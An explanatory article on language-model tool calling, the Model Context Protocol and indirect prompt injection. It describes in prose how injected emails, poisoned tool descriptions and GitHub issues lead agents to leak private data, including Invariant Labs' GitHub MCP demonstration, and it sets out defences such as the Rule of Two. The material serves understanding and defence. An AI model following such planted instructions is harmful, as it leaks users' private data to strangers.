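# Third-party tool calls by language models: how they work, what goes wrong and how they are constrained

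## How a language model calls an outside tool

A large language model is a program that reads text and writes more text. On its own it cannot open a mailbox, look up today's exchange rate or pay a bill, so developers give it tools, which are pieces of ordinary software that do such things, each with a written description for the model to read. When a task needs a tool, the model writes a tool call, a structured request that names the tool and supplies its inputs. The host application, such as ChatGPT or a company's in-house assistant, is the program that runs the model, shows it the tools and executes or forwards its calls. An agent is a model that runs in a loop, calling tools, reading what they return and choosing the next step.

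Many tools are third-party tools, which means someone other than the model's developer or the user wrote them or runs them. That may be a mail provider, an accounting firm or a stranger who publishes code. These tools bring other people's text and code into a process that often has access to the user's accounts.

A language model only writes a request for a tool call, and other software carries it out. With Claude models, either the developer's code or Anthropic's servers perform the operation, according to *How tool use works*, Anthropic's guide for developers. OpenAI's *Function calling*, the equivalent guide for the GPT models, and Microsoft's *Use the functions tool* describe the same split between request and execution. A model can therefore request a payment that nobody wanted, but no money moves until a program with the right credentials acts on the request. If the host, the program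 that receives the model's requests, acts on all of them automatically, each request is in practice a command. In *Agentao*, Jin, Jiao and Tong (2026) build a host around this split, which treats the model's output as a proposal to authorise or refuse. They claim no formal guarantee of safety for the design.

### The loop

Before a model can call a tool, the tool must be defined. Anthropic's *Define tools* lists the three main parts of a definition: a name, a plain-text description of what the tool does and when to use it, and a JSON schema that sets out the inputs. JSON is a text format that stores data as labelled fields inside braces. Anthropic calls detailed descriptions "by far the most important factor in tool performance" and recommends at least three or four sentences for each tool. Descriptions matter because the model cannot see a tool's code. *TRUSTDESC* (Ye, Zhang and colleagues,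 2026) explains that a tool consists of executable code and a description, and that the code stays on the application's side. The model therefore selects tools from their descriptions alone, whether or not these match the code.

The host sends the tool definitions with the user's request, and the provider's software turns them into text. Anthropic places them in the system prompt, the standing instructions at the start of the model's input, before any instructions from the host's developer. OpenAI also inserts them into the system message and charges for them as input. Long lists increase the price and reduce accuracy, so OpenAI suggests fewer than 20 functions at the start of a turn and offers a search tool that lets newer models load more definitions as needed.

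The model then writes its reply, which may be prose, one call or several calls at once. By default the model's output determines whether a call occurs, but a developer can forbid calls and, with many models, require one or force the use of a particular tool. Each call contains an identifier, the tool's name and the arguments. OpenAI's strict mode makes the arguments reliably match the schema, while without it the model matches the schema only on a best-effort basis. Arguments that match the schema can still contain the wrong values. If the schema requires a number and an account code, for example, a payment of the wrong amount to the wrong account satisfies it.

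The host then parses the request, checks it and runs the tool. Its developer decides how much it checks. OpenAI's sample program, which fetches a horoscope, checks that the function's name matches the expected one and then runs it. That is enough for a horoscope, but a developer whose tool moves money would want to add a spending limit, a permissions check or a pause for the user's approval, since the call format provides none of these.

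The tool's output, called the tool result, goes back to the model as text, or sometimes as an image or a file, with the identifier of the call it answers. Errors go back the same way. Anthropic's *Handle tool calls* instructs the host to return the error message as the content of the result, and Claude typically retries an invalid call two or three times with corrections before it apologises to the user. Error messages therefore influence the model's next step as much as successful results do.

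For the next round, the host sends the original messages again, together with the model's reply and the new result. The model can then make another call. The loop ends when a reply has a stop reason other than tool use: a finished answer, a length limit, a preset stop sequence or a refusal. Unless the host trims the record, it grows with each round, so an email the model read in the first round is still part of the model's input in the tenth.

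### An invoice, from mailbox to ledger

Suppose that the owner of a small firm asks her assistant to find the latest invoice from a supplier, Northgate Paper, and enter it in the firm's accounting service. The host offers the model two third-party tools, `find_email` from the mail provider and `create_bill` from the accounting service. (Firm, tools and data are fictitious, and the JSON is a shortened version of Anthropic's format.) The second tool has this definition:

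```json
{
  "name": "create_bill",
  "description": "Records a supplier's invoice as a bill to pay.",
  "input_schema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "supplier": {"type": "string"},
      "amount_eur": {"type": "number"},
      "pay_to": {"type": "string",
                 "description": "The supplier's bank account"}
    },
    "required": ["supplier", "amount_eur", "pay_to"]
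  }
}
```

The accounting service controls every word of it. After reading both definitions and the owner's request, the model writes its first call:

```json
{"type": "tool_use", "id": "call_1", "name": "find_email",
 "input": {"query": "invoice Northgate Paper"}}
```

There is no password in this text. When the owner linked her mailbox, the mail provider issued an access token, a digital credential that lets its bearer use the account. The host attaches that token to the request and sends both to the mail provider, which returns the newest match:

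```json
{"type": "tool_result", "tool_use_id": "call_1",
 "content": "{\"from\": \"billing@northgate.example\",
   \"body\": \"Invoice 2207. Total EUR 480. Pay to 5521-07.\"}"}
```

The mail provider supplies the wrapper. The body is the work of whoever sent the email, which may be Northgate Paper or someone who imitates it. From that body the model takes the values for its second call:

```json
{"type": "tool_use", "id": "call_2", "name": "create_bill",
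 "input": {"supplier": "Northgate Paper",
           "amount_eur": 480, "pay_to": "5521-07"}}
```

The host attaches a different token, for the accounting service, and the service returns confirmation that it has saved the bill. The model reads the confirmation and writes a closing sentence to the owner.

| Step | Who controls the text | Credentials in use |
|---|---|---|
| Tool definitions enter the context | Mail provider and accounting service | The host's own key to the model provider |
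| The owner makes her request | The owner | The same key |
| The model calls `find_email` | The model, on the basis of all the text so far | None in the call itself |
| The host runs `find_email` | The mail provider's code determines what happens | The owner's mailbox token |
| The email returns | The sender of the email, inside the mail provider's wrapper | None; the text goes to the model |
| The model calls `create_bill` | The model, now with the sender's words in its context | None in the call itself |
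| The host runs `create_bill` | The accounting service's code determines what happens | The owner's accounting token |
| The confirmation returns | The accounting service | None; the text goes to the model |

The email can cause two different problems. It may contain a false account number, which is ordinary invoice fraud. In that case the loop works as its designers intended, and a human clerk might make the same payment. Or the email may contain an instruction to the assistant, such as a request to search the mailbox for the bank's last ten messages and copy them into the bill. The owner did not ask for this, but the assistant has both tools it needs to do it.

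In its guide, OpenAI tells developers not to make the model fill in arguments that the application already knows. OpenAI presents this as a way to reduce the model's work, but it also helps protect against the first danger. If the host takes `pay_to` from the firm's supplier records, no wording in an email can change it, because the model never writes that value.

### Where the tool runs and whose account it uses

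In the example, both tools ran on their suppliers' servers. Other tools run on the user's machine, or wherever the host application runs. These include functions that a developer writes for one application, which Anthropic says make up the vast majority of tool traffic. They also include a handful of common tools for running shell commands, editing files or controlling a browser. Anthropic publishes the schemas for these tools, and the host application runs them. A shell tool usually has the same permissions as the program that starts it, so on a personal laptop without further restrictions, it can have access to all of the user's files.

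The model's provider runs some tools on its own servers. At Anthropic these are web search, web page retrieval, code execution and the search for further tools. The provider's system may search and read several times before it returns anything, and the host usually receives the record of calls only after they have finished. In that case, a developer cannot inspect each request before it runs and has to rely on the provider's controls.

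When a tool runs on a third party's servers, either the host or the provider can send the call. OpenAI's guide to remote tools describes a setup in which the provider sends it. The developer supplies the address of a server that follows the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that host applications use to find and call outside tools. OpenAI's system fetches the list of tools from that server, forwards the model's calls to it and adds the answers to the model's context. By default, it asks for approval before sharing any data with the server, but the developer can turn this off. OpenAI has not verified these servers and warns that a malicious one can extract sensitive data from anything that enters the model's context.

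A tool that runs on the user's own machine can still be a package by an unknown author. Running locally gives it rights that a remote service would never get.

The credentials mostly belong to the user. The usual method is OAuth, a standard that lets a person give one program access to their account at another service without sharing their password. According to OpenAI's *Authentication*, the host, ChatGPT or the coding agent Codex, obtains the token on the user's behalf. OpenAI's *App Security Whitepaper* adds that after an administrator installs a custom tool for a company, each employee must still link their own account before using it. This keeps one employee's assistant out of another's files. The accounting service in the example therefore receives a valid request from a genuine customer, but the token does not show whether the customer's wish or a stranger's email prompted the call.

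Tokens carry scopes, which are named permissions and can be broader than the task requires. OpenAI's built-in Gmail connector has five tools that search or read messages, and all five need the scope `gmail.modify`. The tools limit the model to reading, but the token would also permit changes to the mailbox. This departs from the principle of least privilege, under which a program gets only the permissions its task needs. The comparable Outlook tools need only `Mail.Read`. OpenAI has deprecated these connectors for models released after September 1, 2026, and directs developers to MCP servers, but existing models still support them.

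### How models learned to call tools

Researchers had built the parts of this loop before companies sold it. Jin and colleagues start the history with MRKL, in which a language model passes parts of a problem to specialised modules such as a calculator. Toolformer trained a model to decide when and how to call calculators, search engines, translation systems and calendars, using self-supervised signals, which come from the data itself rather than from human labels. ReAct contributed a cycle much like that of the commercial loop, in which the model writes some reasoning, takes an action in its environment, then reasons again. Jin and colleagues credit ReAct with better performance on knowledge-heavy and interactive tasks, and with behaviour that was easier to interpret.

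In an early commercial format, preserved in Anthropic's *Legacy tool use*, the developer wrote the tool definitions into the prompt by hand, and Anthropic recommended no more than three to five of them. Function calling, as OpenAI named the feature, made tool definitions a standard part of the interface. The developer now passes a list of tools in a separate field, and the provider writes the prompt text.

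The provider can do that well because it has trained the model on the format. OpenAI inserts functions "in a syntax the model has been trained on". Anthropic has also trained Claude on thousands of successful trajectories (complete records of a task from request to outcome) that use the exact signatures of its published shell, file and browser tools. Anthropic says Claude calls these tools more reliably than custom tools that do the same job, and recovers from errors better. Developers can also use reinforcement learning, letting a model practise on live tools and rewarding the runs that succeed.

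A model learns the call format in training, so it usually follows it, but not always. For developers who need certainty about the format, OpenAI adds mechanisms outside the model, such as strict mode and, for tools that take free text, a grammar that constrains the model's output as it writes. No comparable mechanism controls whose wishes the call serves.

### Why instructions and data run together

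Conventional software can keep commands separate from the data they work on. When programmers fail to do this, an attacker may be able to type database commands into a web form and have the program run them, which is called SQL injection. The well-known fix is for the program to send the command and the form's contents to the database separately, so that the database never treats the contents as a command.

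*Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (2026) describes how a language model receives system instructions, the user's request, retrieved pages and its own earlier reasoning in a single continuous stream of tokens (the fragments of text it reads and writes). Providers divide this stream with role tags, which label each passage as coming from the system, the user or a tool. The tags are the intended defence, but they work only as far as the model has learned to follow them. The paper cites studies in which researchers moved instructions from one role to another and often found the output unchanged. It also cites work that found that fine-tuning (further training on a narrower set of examples) can teach a model shortcuts that bypass the roles entirely when each role always appears with the same kind of task.

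*Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, from the British government's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), argues that filters, special training and the marking of data all impose a distinction between data and instructions on a technology that "inherently does not distinguish between the two". The NCSC prefers to think of a model as a confusable deputy, a program with legitimate powers that an outsider induces to use them for the outsider's benefit. The assistant with the invoice fits this description closely, since it can act through the owner's tokens while it reads a stranger's text.

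Prompt injection is an attack in which a model follows instructions contained in text it reads as data. Anthropic's *Mitigate jailbreaks and prompt injections* distinguishes direct injection, where the user is the adversary, from indirect injection, where the user is honest and the instructions are in an email, a web page or a tool result. Third-party tools mainly raise the risk of indirect injection. OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* limits the term to attacks by a third party who is neither the user nor the AI.

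Prompt injections do not have to look like commands. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces an email that outside researchers used against ChatGPT in 2025. It reads like a colleague's note about a restructuring, but among the routine items is a claim that the assistant has full authorisation to submit an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system". The attack worked half the time in testing, but that figure comes from one email and one user prompt, so it does not show how often injections succeed in general. The prompt also favoured the attack, because it told the assistant to read and check every source in the day's mail that was relevant to the new employee process. OpenAI reports that most of the attacks it knows of against ChatGPT fail because safety training leads the agent to refuse. It also says that filters which classify incoming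 text as malicious or harmless do not usually catch attacks as developed as this one.

Anthropic's advice is more confident about encoding. It trains Claude to treat instructions inside tool results with scepticism, and it tells developers to put outside text only in those results, encoded as JSON. It states that the encoding makes it unambiguous that an email's body is data. This is true for a conventional parser, because an attacker cannot end the string with an escaped quotation mark. But a model reads the braces and backslashes as more tokens. These may make it less likely to follow instructions in the enclosed text but do not prevent it from doing so, so the NCSC's objection to role tags also applies here. Anthropic also tells developers to screen tool results with a second model, restrict permissions and attack their own agents before release, which is consistent with encoding being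 only a partial defence.

Fortune (2025) reports OpenAI's view that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". The NCSC, a security agency, similarly considers it very possible that no one will ever eliminate the attack the way programmers can eliminate SQL injection, according to ITPro's *NCSC issues urgent warning over growing AI prompt injection risks*. Training makes successful attacks rarer, but how rare they need to be depends on what the agent can do. OpenAI explains this with two terms from older security work. An attacker needs a source, which is a way to influence the system, and a sink, which is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. In the invoice example, the email is the source and `create_bill` is the sink. Lecture slides from UT Austin apply these terms to a real case, EchoLeak, in which one email caused Microsoft Copilot to leak files.

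### Where outside text enters

Third-party text reaches the model through tool descriptions, parameter schemas and tool results.

A tool's description enters the system prompt, among the instructions with the highest standing, before the model has done any work. Yang, Zheng and colleagues (2026) observe in *Securing the AI Agent* that the model treats the description as trusted context. Prompt injection in a description or in a tool's other metadata is called tool poisoning. Ye and colleagues illustrate it with a file-upload tool whose description contains instructions to read the user's private login key first, pass it along as a "note", and not mention having done so. A description can also mislead the model without containing any improper instructions. Ye and colleagues found that a documentation tool from one MCP server, exa-mcp-server, advertised the "highest quality" and "freshest context",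 and that a model might choose it even when the user had asked for a competitor, Context7. A scanner that looks for hidden commands would not flag such a description.

Parameter schemas receive less attention, although they too consist largely of words: field names, explanatory notes, permitted values and sometimes worked examples. A schema also specifies what data the model should send. In the poisoned upload tool, the key leaves the machine through the `note` field. The accounting service in the invoice example could add a required field called `recent_correspondence`, with a remark that it helps to detect fraud, and a model trying to satisfy the schema might well fill it from the mailbox. OpenAI warns that operators of MCP servers, who write their own tool definitions, can request data that a developer would not want to share, and gives this as its reason for requiring approval of each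 call by default.

An attacker must supply a tool or tamper with it to poison its description or schema, but can put text into a result by writing something that an honest tool will later fetch, such as an email, a web page or a customer's comment. Making access to private data read-only gives little protection. OpenAI gives the example of an agent with web access and a read-only connection to a company's customer database. A web page contains instructions to look up a customer and put that customer's email address into a web link. When the agent fetches the link, the address goes to whoever runs the site, without any change to the database. OpenAI's remedy is to split the job into two requests. The first has only web search and collects the public facts, and the second has only the customer database and receives those facts as text.

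## The Model Context Protocol: a common interface for tools

In the invoice example, the host already knew how to reach the mail provider and the accounting service. Until late 2024, developers usually had to write a separate connection for each pair of application and service. Ten assistants and twenty services would need 200 connections, but if all thirty follow one standard, each needs only one implementation. Anthropic released MCP as an open standard on 25 November 2024 to end this duplication. *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* (Anthropic, 2024) says that every new data source had required its own custom implementation.

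OpenAI and Google DeepMind, two of Anthropic's main competitors, later adopted the protocol, according to the French trade article *Le protocole MCP (Model Context Protocol), norme open source régissant les interactions* (2026). *What's New in MCP in 2026* (2026), from the software engineering newsletter Strategize Your Career, reports that the Agentic AI Foundation, part of the non-profit Linux Foundation, now governs the protocol. A group of Core Maintainers decides which proposals enter the specification. The two lead maintainers, David Soria Parra and Den Delimarsky, both work at Anthropic, so its staff still have a leading role.

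The Model Context Protocol (2026) project announced close to half a billion monthly downloads of its main software development kits (SDKs), the code libraries programmers use to build MCP software, when the current version came out on 28 July 2026. The TypeScript and Python SDKs had each passed one billion total downloads. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports a slightly lower figure of over 400 million a month, a fourfold increase this year.

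These numbers count copies of software, not people or tool calls. An automated build system may download the same library many times a day, while one copy on a company's server may handle requests from thousands of employees. Anthropic also lists over 950 servers in Claude's directory and says that millions of people use them every day, but it doesn't give the number of calls. In the release announcement, Honeycomb, a software monitoring company, gave a figure closer to actual use, saying that agents now make nearly 20% of the interactive queries on its service each month.

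### Hosts, clients and servers

The host, such as Claude Desktop or a code editor, contains a client that manages the connection to a server, the program that offers the tools. The model writes its tool call in its provider's format, and the client turns that into an MCP request. A developer can therefore change the model without rewriting the server.

A local server runs on the user's machine. The host starts it as a process and exchanges messages with it over standard input and output, the text channels that an operating system gives every program. *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* (Willison, 2024) describes Claude Desktop working this way at launch. A remote server runs elsewhere and receives its messages over HTTP, the protocol of the web. Companies often put a gateway, a program that forwards, counts or blocks requests, in front of remote servers. Messages sent to a local server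 over standard input don't pass through this gateway.

A local server can also listen for HTTP, in which case a website open in the user's browser may be able to contact it. To prevent this, Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP* (2026) requires servers to check the header where the browser records which site a request came from.

### Listing and calling tools

MCP messages follow JSON-RPC, a convention for requests and replies in JSON. The client sends `tools/list`, and the server returns its tool definitions, which the host passes to the model. When the model asks to record the invoice from Northgate Paper, the client sends `tools/call`:

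```http
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Content-Type: application/json
Accept: application/json, text/event-stream
MCP-Protocol-Version: 2026-07-28
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: create_bill

{"jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 2, "method": "tools/call",
 "params": {
   "name": "create_bill",
   "arguments": {"supplier": "Northgate Paper",
                 "amount_eur": 480, "pay_to": "5521-07"},
   "_meta": {
     "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28",
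     "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities":
       {"elicitation": {}}}}}
```

The example omits the headers for the server's address and the owner's access token. The word `elicitation` tells the server that this client can put questions to the user. The server replies:

```json
{"jsonrpc": "2.0", "id": 2,
 "result": {"resultType": "complete",
   "content": [{"type": "text",
                "text": "Bill saved: Northgate Paper, EUR 480."}],
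   "isError": false}}
```

The host gives the text in `content` to the model as the tool result.

Two servers may each offer a tool with the same name, such as `search`. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) recommends that clients tell them apart by adding a prefix for each server. The prefix should not be the name a server gives itself, because two servers can choose the same name. The protocol also doesn't verify these names, so a stranger's server can present itself under an accounting service's name. Under the general rules in Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026), the names are for display, logging and debugging, and implementations should not rely on them for security decisions.

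### The revision of July 2026

In the previous version, from November 2025, the client and server began with a handshake in which they exchanged protocol versions and capabilities. The server could then issue a session identifier, which the client had to attach to every later request. Large services run many copies of a server behind a load balancer, which spreads requests among them, but a session tied the client to the copy that held the session in memory. Google's *Scaling AI Agent Infrastructure with the MCP Stateless updates* (2026) describes this as a "hard wall" for the company's cloud systems and reports that requests failed because the server could not find the session.

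The July revision removed the handshake and the session. Each request now includes its protocol version and the client's capabilities in the `_meta` field, and a server must reject a request that lacks them. Any copy of the server can answer any request, so a client no longer depends on one copy staying up. A gateway can interpret each request without a record of the earlier ones.

A client could previously resume a reply that broke off partway. According to the changelog of the Model Context Protocol (2026), a broken reply stream now loses the call, and the client must send it again under a new identifier. If the accounting service saved the bill just before the connection dropped, the repeated call could create a second bill unless the service recognises duplicates itself.

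Some tools still need to remember things between calls, such as the contents of a shopping basket. The server now returns an identifier for the basket, and the model includes it in later calls. The Model Context Protocol (2026) maintainers argue in their post on the release candidate that this is often more powerful than a hidden session, because the model can see the identifier and pass it from one tool to another. However, an injected instruction could also tell the model to send the identifier elsewhere. The specification therefore advises servers with a login to check on every call that the caller may use the basket. It advises servers without one to make the identifier hard to guess and limit its lifetime. Akamai, which sells security services, says the revision ends session hijacking at the protocol level but lists application-managed state among the new openings for abuse.

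For remote calls, the method and the tool's name now also appear in HTTP headers, the labelled lines at the top of a request. A gateway can therefore block `create_bill` for trainees without reading the body. Without a further check, a hostile client could name a harmless tool in the header, which the gateway would approve, and `create_bill` in the body, which the server would run. Servers must therefore reject any request whose header and body don't match. A gateway that reads only headers depends on the server to make that comparison.

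A server can also mark chosen arguments in a tool's schema, and the client must then copy their values into headers. The Agentic AI Foundation suggests that a gateway could use these headers to route or limit traffic by values such as region, tenant or priority. They are less useful for controlling payments, because the rules exclude arguments of the JSON type `number`. The accounting service would have to redefine `amount_eur`, perhaps as a whole number of cents, before exposing it. The rules also advise against exposing passwords, tokens or personal data, since every intermediary can read the headers. A gateway that enforces a spending limit or checks results for hidden instructions still has to read the bodies.

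Tool lists can now be cached. A reply to `tools/list` specifies how long it stays fresh and whether a shared cache may store it, and servers should return unchanged lists in the same order. Clients make fewer requests, and model providers can reuse more of their earlier processing of the prompt. A gateway that stores lists has to respect the sharing label. If a server mistakenly marks an administrator's list as `public`, the gateway might serve it to ordinary staff. Gustavo (2026), in *The 2026-07-28 MCP Spec*, a checklist for developers, therefore treats the scope of a cache as a matter of security as well as compatibility. Caching can also leave clients with outdated tool descriptions, for up to five minutes if that is the list's lifetime and the client has not subscribed to change notices.

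The revision also changed how a server asks the user for input during a call. Suppose the accounting service needs to ask the owner about account 5521-07, which is new for Northgate Paper. Previously, it would have sent the question over a connection that had to stay open. Now it ends the call with a result of type `input_required`, which contains the question. The host asks the owner, and the client repeats the original call with her answer. Any copy of the server can handle the repeated call, because the `requestState` field contains whatever the server needs to continue. That field passes through the client, so Model Context Protocol's *Multi Round-Trip Requests* (2026) tells servers to treat it as attacker-controlled input and to protect it against tampering wherever it affects permissions or business logic.

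A server may now ask such questions only while it is processing a request from the client. Supabase, a database company, plans to have users confirm the cost of a new project or a query that would delete data. But an answer does not prove that a person gave it. Model Context Protocol's *Multi-Round-Trip Results* explains that with the official Ruby library, a developer registers a handler, and the client then answers the server and repeats the call automatically. A developer could write a handler that always accepts.

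### What the protocol leaves to implementers

The specification uses MUST for requirements and SHOULD for recommendations, which an implementer may depart from for good reason. It only recommends that a human be able to refuse tool calls, as did the first version of the Model Context Protocol (2024). It leaves the design of the interface to the host's developer. A `tools/call` request has no standard field to show whether anyone approved it, so the accounting service cannot distinguish a payment the owner confirmed from one the host sent automatically.

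The protocol also has few rules for checking tool descriptions. Servers can attach annotations to a tool, such as "read-only" or "destructive". Clients MUST treat these as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server, but the rules for tools do not specify how to decide which servers to trust. They also do not require clients to scan the description that the model reads. When a server changes its tools, it should notify clients that have subscribed to such notices, but clients need not ask the user to approve the new descriptions.

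Clients SHOULD also log tool use for later audits. The maintainers have deprecated the protocol's own feature for sending log messages from servers to clients. They direct developers of remote servers to OpenTelemetry, an existing standard for recording operations across systems. The July revision specifies the names of the fields that link these records. An operator can follow a call from the host to the server and beyond if each program on the way keeps records.

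The specification places most of its binding requirements for tools on servers, which MUST validate inputs, control access, limit the rate of calls and sanitise outputs. It only recommends that clients confirm sensitive operations, show the inputs to the user before a call and check results before the model reads them. This division is awkward when strangers supply the tools, because a malicious server will not follow these requirements and the client is best placed to protect the user.

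### For and against the flexibility

There are practical reasons to leave these decisions open. A weather lookup and a bank transfer need different treatment, and an agent that runs overnight may have nobody available to approve its calls. If the protocol required a click for every call, a server could not check that the host complied, because it has no access to the host's interface.

Platforms and companies can add controls that match their own risks. In *MCP security isn't inevitable*, Stanley points to Microsoft's plans for a Windows registry of MCP servers, with requirements such as code signing, declared privileges and limits on silent changes to tool definitions. Microsoft's *MCP Security Gateway* specifies a gateway that subjects calls to rate limits and approval, scans replies for threats and compares tool schemas with a stored baseline. If any component fails, the gateway must refuse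 the call.

A host can support MCP without having any of these protections, so a buyer who sees "Supports MCP" on a product page can't know whether the application will ask before it pays a bill. An Internet-Draft submitted to the IETF, the body behind many internet standards, attributes several classes of vulnerability to a lack of binding security requirements in the MCP specification. The draft is an individual's proposal and does not have the IETF's endorsement. Its claim is too broad, since the duties of servers are binding, but it is a fair criticism of the rules on consent. The US National Security Agency has made its own criticisms, which a later section covers.

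The July revision weakens the case for leaving so much open. The maintainers made it compulsory to match headers with bodies and to protect a sensitive `requestState`, and software can test both without dictating what the user sees. They could likewise require clients to hold back a tool whose description has changed until a person or a company policy approves it, but no protocol could ensure that the person had read the new description.

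### Changes since July 2026

The July version was still current in late November 2026. *A More Predictable Release Cycle for MCP* (Delimarsky and Soria Parra, 2026) announced that new versions will generally appear on the last Tuesday of March and September, starting on 30 March 2027. This changed how releases are prepared but not the protocol's messages. In August, *The New MCP Roadmap* (Soria Parra and Delimarsky, 2026) had set out the priorities for the next version, including a standard way for servers to recognise agents acting for a user who is not present. The current authorisation process assumes that a person will approve access in a browser.

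On 10 November, the Model Context Protocol (2026) blog described a draft extension for file transfers that is more explicit about consent than the core rules for tools. Before a file leaves, the host gets the user's approval or, if no user is present, applies a policy for the agent. The client fills in the file argument so the model does not have to. The extension is optional and has no reference implementation yet, though the working group expects to finish it before the end of the year.

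## GitHub's tool server: instructions hidden in returned data

In May 2025 Invariant Labs, a security company in Zurich, demonstrated an indirect prompt injection that used GitHub's official MCP server. GitHub is a website where programmers store code in repositories, project folders that keep a history of every change. Anyone with an account can file an issue, a bug report or suggestion, on a public repository. Programmers propose changes to the code by opening pull requests. The MCP server lets an assistant read issues and files and open pull requests through tool calls. As heise online's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains, the server works with the user's own account, so the assistant can also read the user's private repositories.

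### From a bug report to a public page

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes a demonstration by Marco Milanta and Luca Beurer-Kellner on an account they had set up for it. The account had a public repository containing a Pac-Man game and several private ones containing personal projects and sensitive information about the owner. The owner used Claude Desktop, running Claude 4 Opus, with the GitHub server connected.

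The attack began when an outsider opened an issue on the game's repository. The outsider worded it as a friendly suggestion to give the project's owner more recognition, and asked for details that the assistant could find only in the owner's other repositories. Nothing happened until the owner asked Claude to look at the open issues. Claude called the tool that fetches them, and the server returned the outsider's text along with the rest. Claude then read the owner's private repositories and put what it found in a pull request on the game's repository. That repository was public, so anyone could read the name of a private project, the owner's plan to move to South America and the owner's salary.

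Every tool in this chain worked as designed. GitHub accepted an issue from a stranger, as it does on any public repository. The server returned the text of the issue, then the private files, which the owner's token allowed it to read. It opened the pull request because the owner was allowed to open one. Unlike tool poisoning, the attack required no change to any tool's description. The model made the wrong calls, and GitHub, like the accounting service in the invoice example, had no way to detect that the owner didn't want them.

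The owner's one chance to stop the leak was the confirmation that Claude Desktop requests by default for each tool call. A careful owner might have wondered why a question about a game required private files. Invariant Labs says that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching, but it gives no figure, and DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* reports the claim as the researchers' suspicion.

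In its post, which includes no statement from GitHub, Invariant Labs says the flaw is not in the server's code and that GitHub alone cannot remove it with a patch, because any agent that uses the server is exposed, whatever its model. Invariant Labs recommends limiting the agent to the repositories it needs and monitoring its calls. It also offers a product that enforces such limits. A sample rule in the post blocks an agent that has used one repository from making calls to any other for the rest of the session.

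That rule would have stopped the demonstration, since Claude had to move from the game to the private repositories. It would also prevent an owner from getting help with two related projects at once. The rule covers only calls to GitHub, so if the agent also had an email tool, an instruction planted in a repository could make it email that repository's contents without breaking the rule.

### The lethal trifecta

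Simon Willison, the software developer who coined the term "prompt injection", calls the combination of capabilities that made the leak possible the "lethal trifecta". *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) lists them as access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally that an attacker could use to steal data. An agent with all three can read an attacker's instruction, collect the requested data and send it out. GitHub's server provided all three by itself, through private repositories, public issues and pull requests respectively.

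Willison had collected dozens of similar attacks on products including ChatGPT, Slack and Microsoft Copilot. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by closing the route through which the data left. But a vendor cannot do this for a user who connects one company's mail tool to another company's web tool. MCP encourages such combinations, and Willison advises users who make them to avoid having all three capabilities together.

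He distrusts products that claim to detect injections. He argues that a filter that catches 95% of attacks is a failure in web security, and that an attacker can phrase the same instruction in endless ways. His own remedy also makes some tools less useful. An email assistant has private data and untrusted content in the same inbox, and it is of limited use if it cannot send a reply.

### Meta's Rule of Two

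Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns the idea into a design rule, and credits both Willison and a similar policy for the Chromium browser. Until researchers find a reliable way to detect and refuse prompt injection, Meta says, an agent should have no more than two of these properties within a session:

- it can process untrustworthy inputs;
- it can have access to sensitive systems or private data;
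- it can change state or communicate externally.

Changing state means altering something outside the conversation, for example by deleting a file or making a payment. A session lasts as long as the agent keeps the same context. An agent that needs all three properties in one session should not work autonomously. At a minimum, its actions must be approved by a person or pass another reliable check.

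The assistant in the GitHub demonstration had all three. Its owner could have removed any one of them, with different results.

| Property removed | Change to the assistant | What a planted instruction could still do |
|---|---|---|
| Untrustworthy inputs | It reads issues only from trusted contributors | Nothing, unless an attacker's text arrives through a trusted contributor |
| Private data | Its token covers only the public repository | Propose or make harmful changes to the game |
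| Changing state and communicating | The owner approves every pull request | Distort the assistant's summary of the issues |

Meta also allows an agent to change its configuration partway through a task. It might browse the web without access to private data, then lose its outside connections before it opens internal systems. The GitHub assistant would read the public issues first, then give up the ability to open pull requests before it accessed a private repository.

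mbgsec's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), a security blogger's reply, welcomes the hard boundaries and Meta's open admission that prompt injection remains unsolved. The advantage of such boundaries is that they do not depend on the model recognising an attack. An assistant whose token covers only the game cannot leak the owner's salary from a private repository, however persuasive the issue is.

### Where the two rules fall short

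An attacker can do damage without taking any data. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) describes a scenario in which a user asks an assistant to check for urgent emails. An instruction hidden in a marketing email tells the assistant to mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the summary, so the user misses the deadline. Willison's lethal trifecta does not cover this case, because he defined it for data theft. Meta's rule covers it because marking a message as read changes state.

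But Meta's rule also has a gap. Its diagram, as Conffab's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) describes it, labels every pair of properties "Safe". Suppose the GitHub assistant can read issues from strangers and edit the game directly, but has no access to private repositories. An injected instruction could make it add malicious code, which people who download the game would run. The rule would flag this design only if the developer counted a public repository as a sensitive system, and a developer who thinks mainly about secrets might not. In its text, Meta is more careful. It promises only to avoid the "highest impact consequences" of prompt injection and warns that designs which satisfy the rule can still fail.

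An agent that cannot take actions can still mislead its owner into taking a harmful one. If it reads a stranger's text and the owner's private files, then reports that a harmful pull request is safe, the owner may accept it. Meta lists misinformation in the agent's answer among the "lower consequence" outcomes that the rule does not address. That label is reasonable for a wrong travel tip, but less so for a wrong code review or a wrong account number on an invoice.

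The limit to one session also has a weakness, because many agents save notes or instruction files and read them again later. An injected instruction saved in one of these files can take effect in a later session that seems to contain no untrusted input. *AutoRedClaw* (2026), a set of tests for agents, includes attacks through such stored material. To apply the rule properly, a developer would also have to treat anything an agent wrote after reading a stranger's text as untrusted.

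When a task needs all three properties, the rule falls back on human approval, which fails if the person approves without reading. Meta acknowledges this and adds that approval may be disruptive or ineffective for agents that run in the background. It hopes other AI systems will eventually supervise such agents, but that would bring back the dependence on a model's judgement that the rule was meant to avoid.

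### How often the attacks succeed

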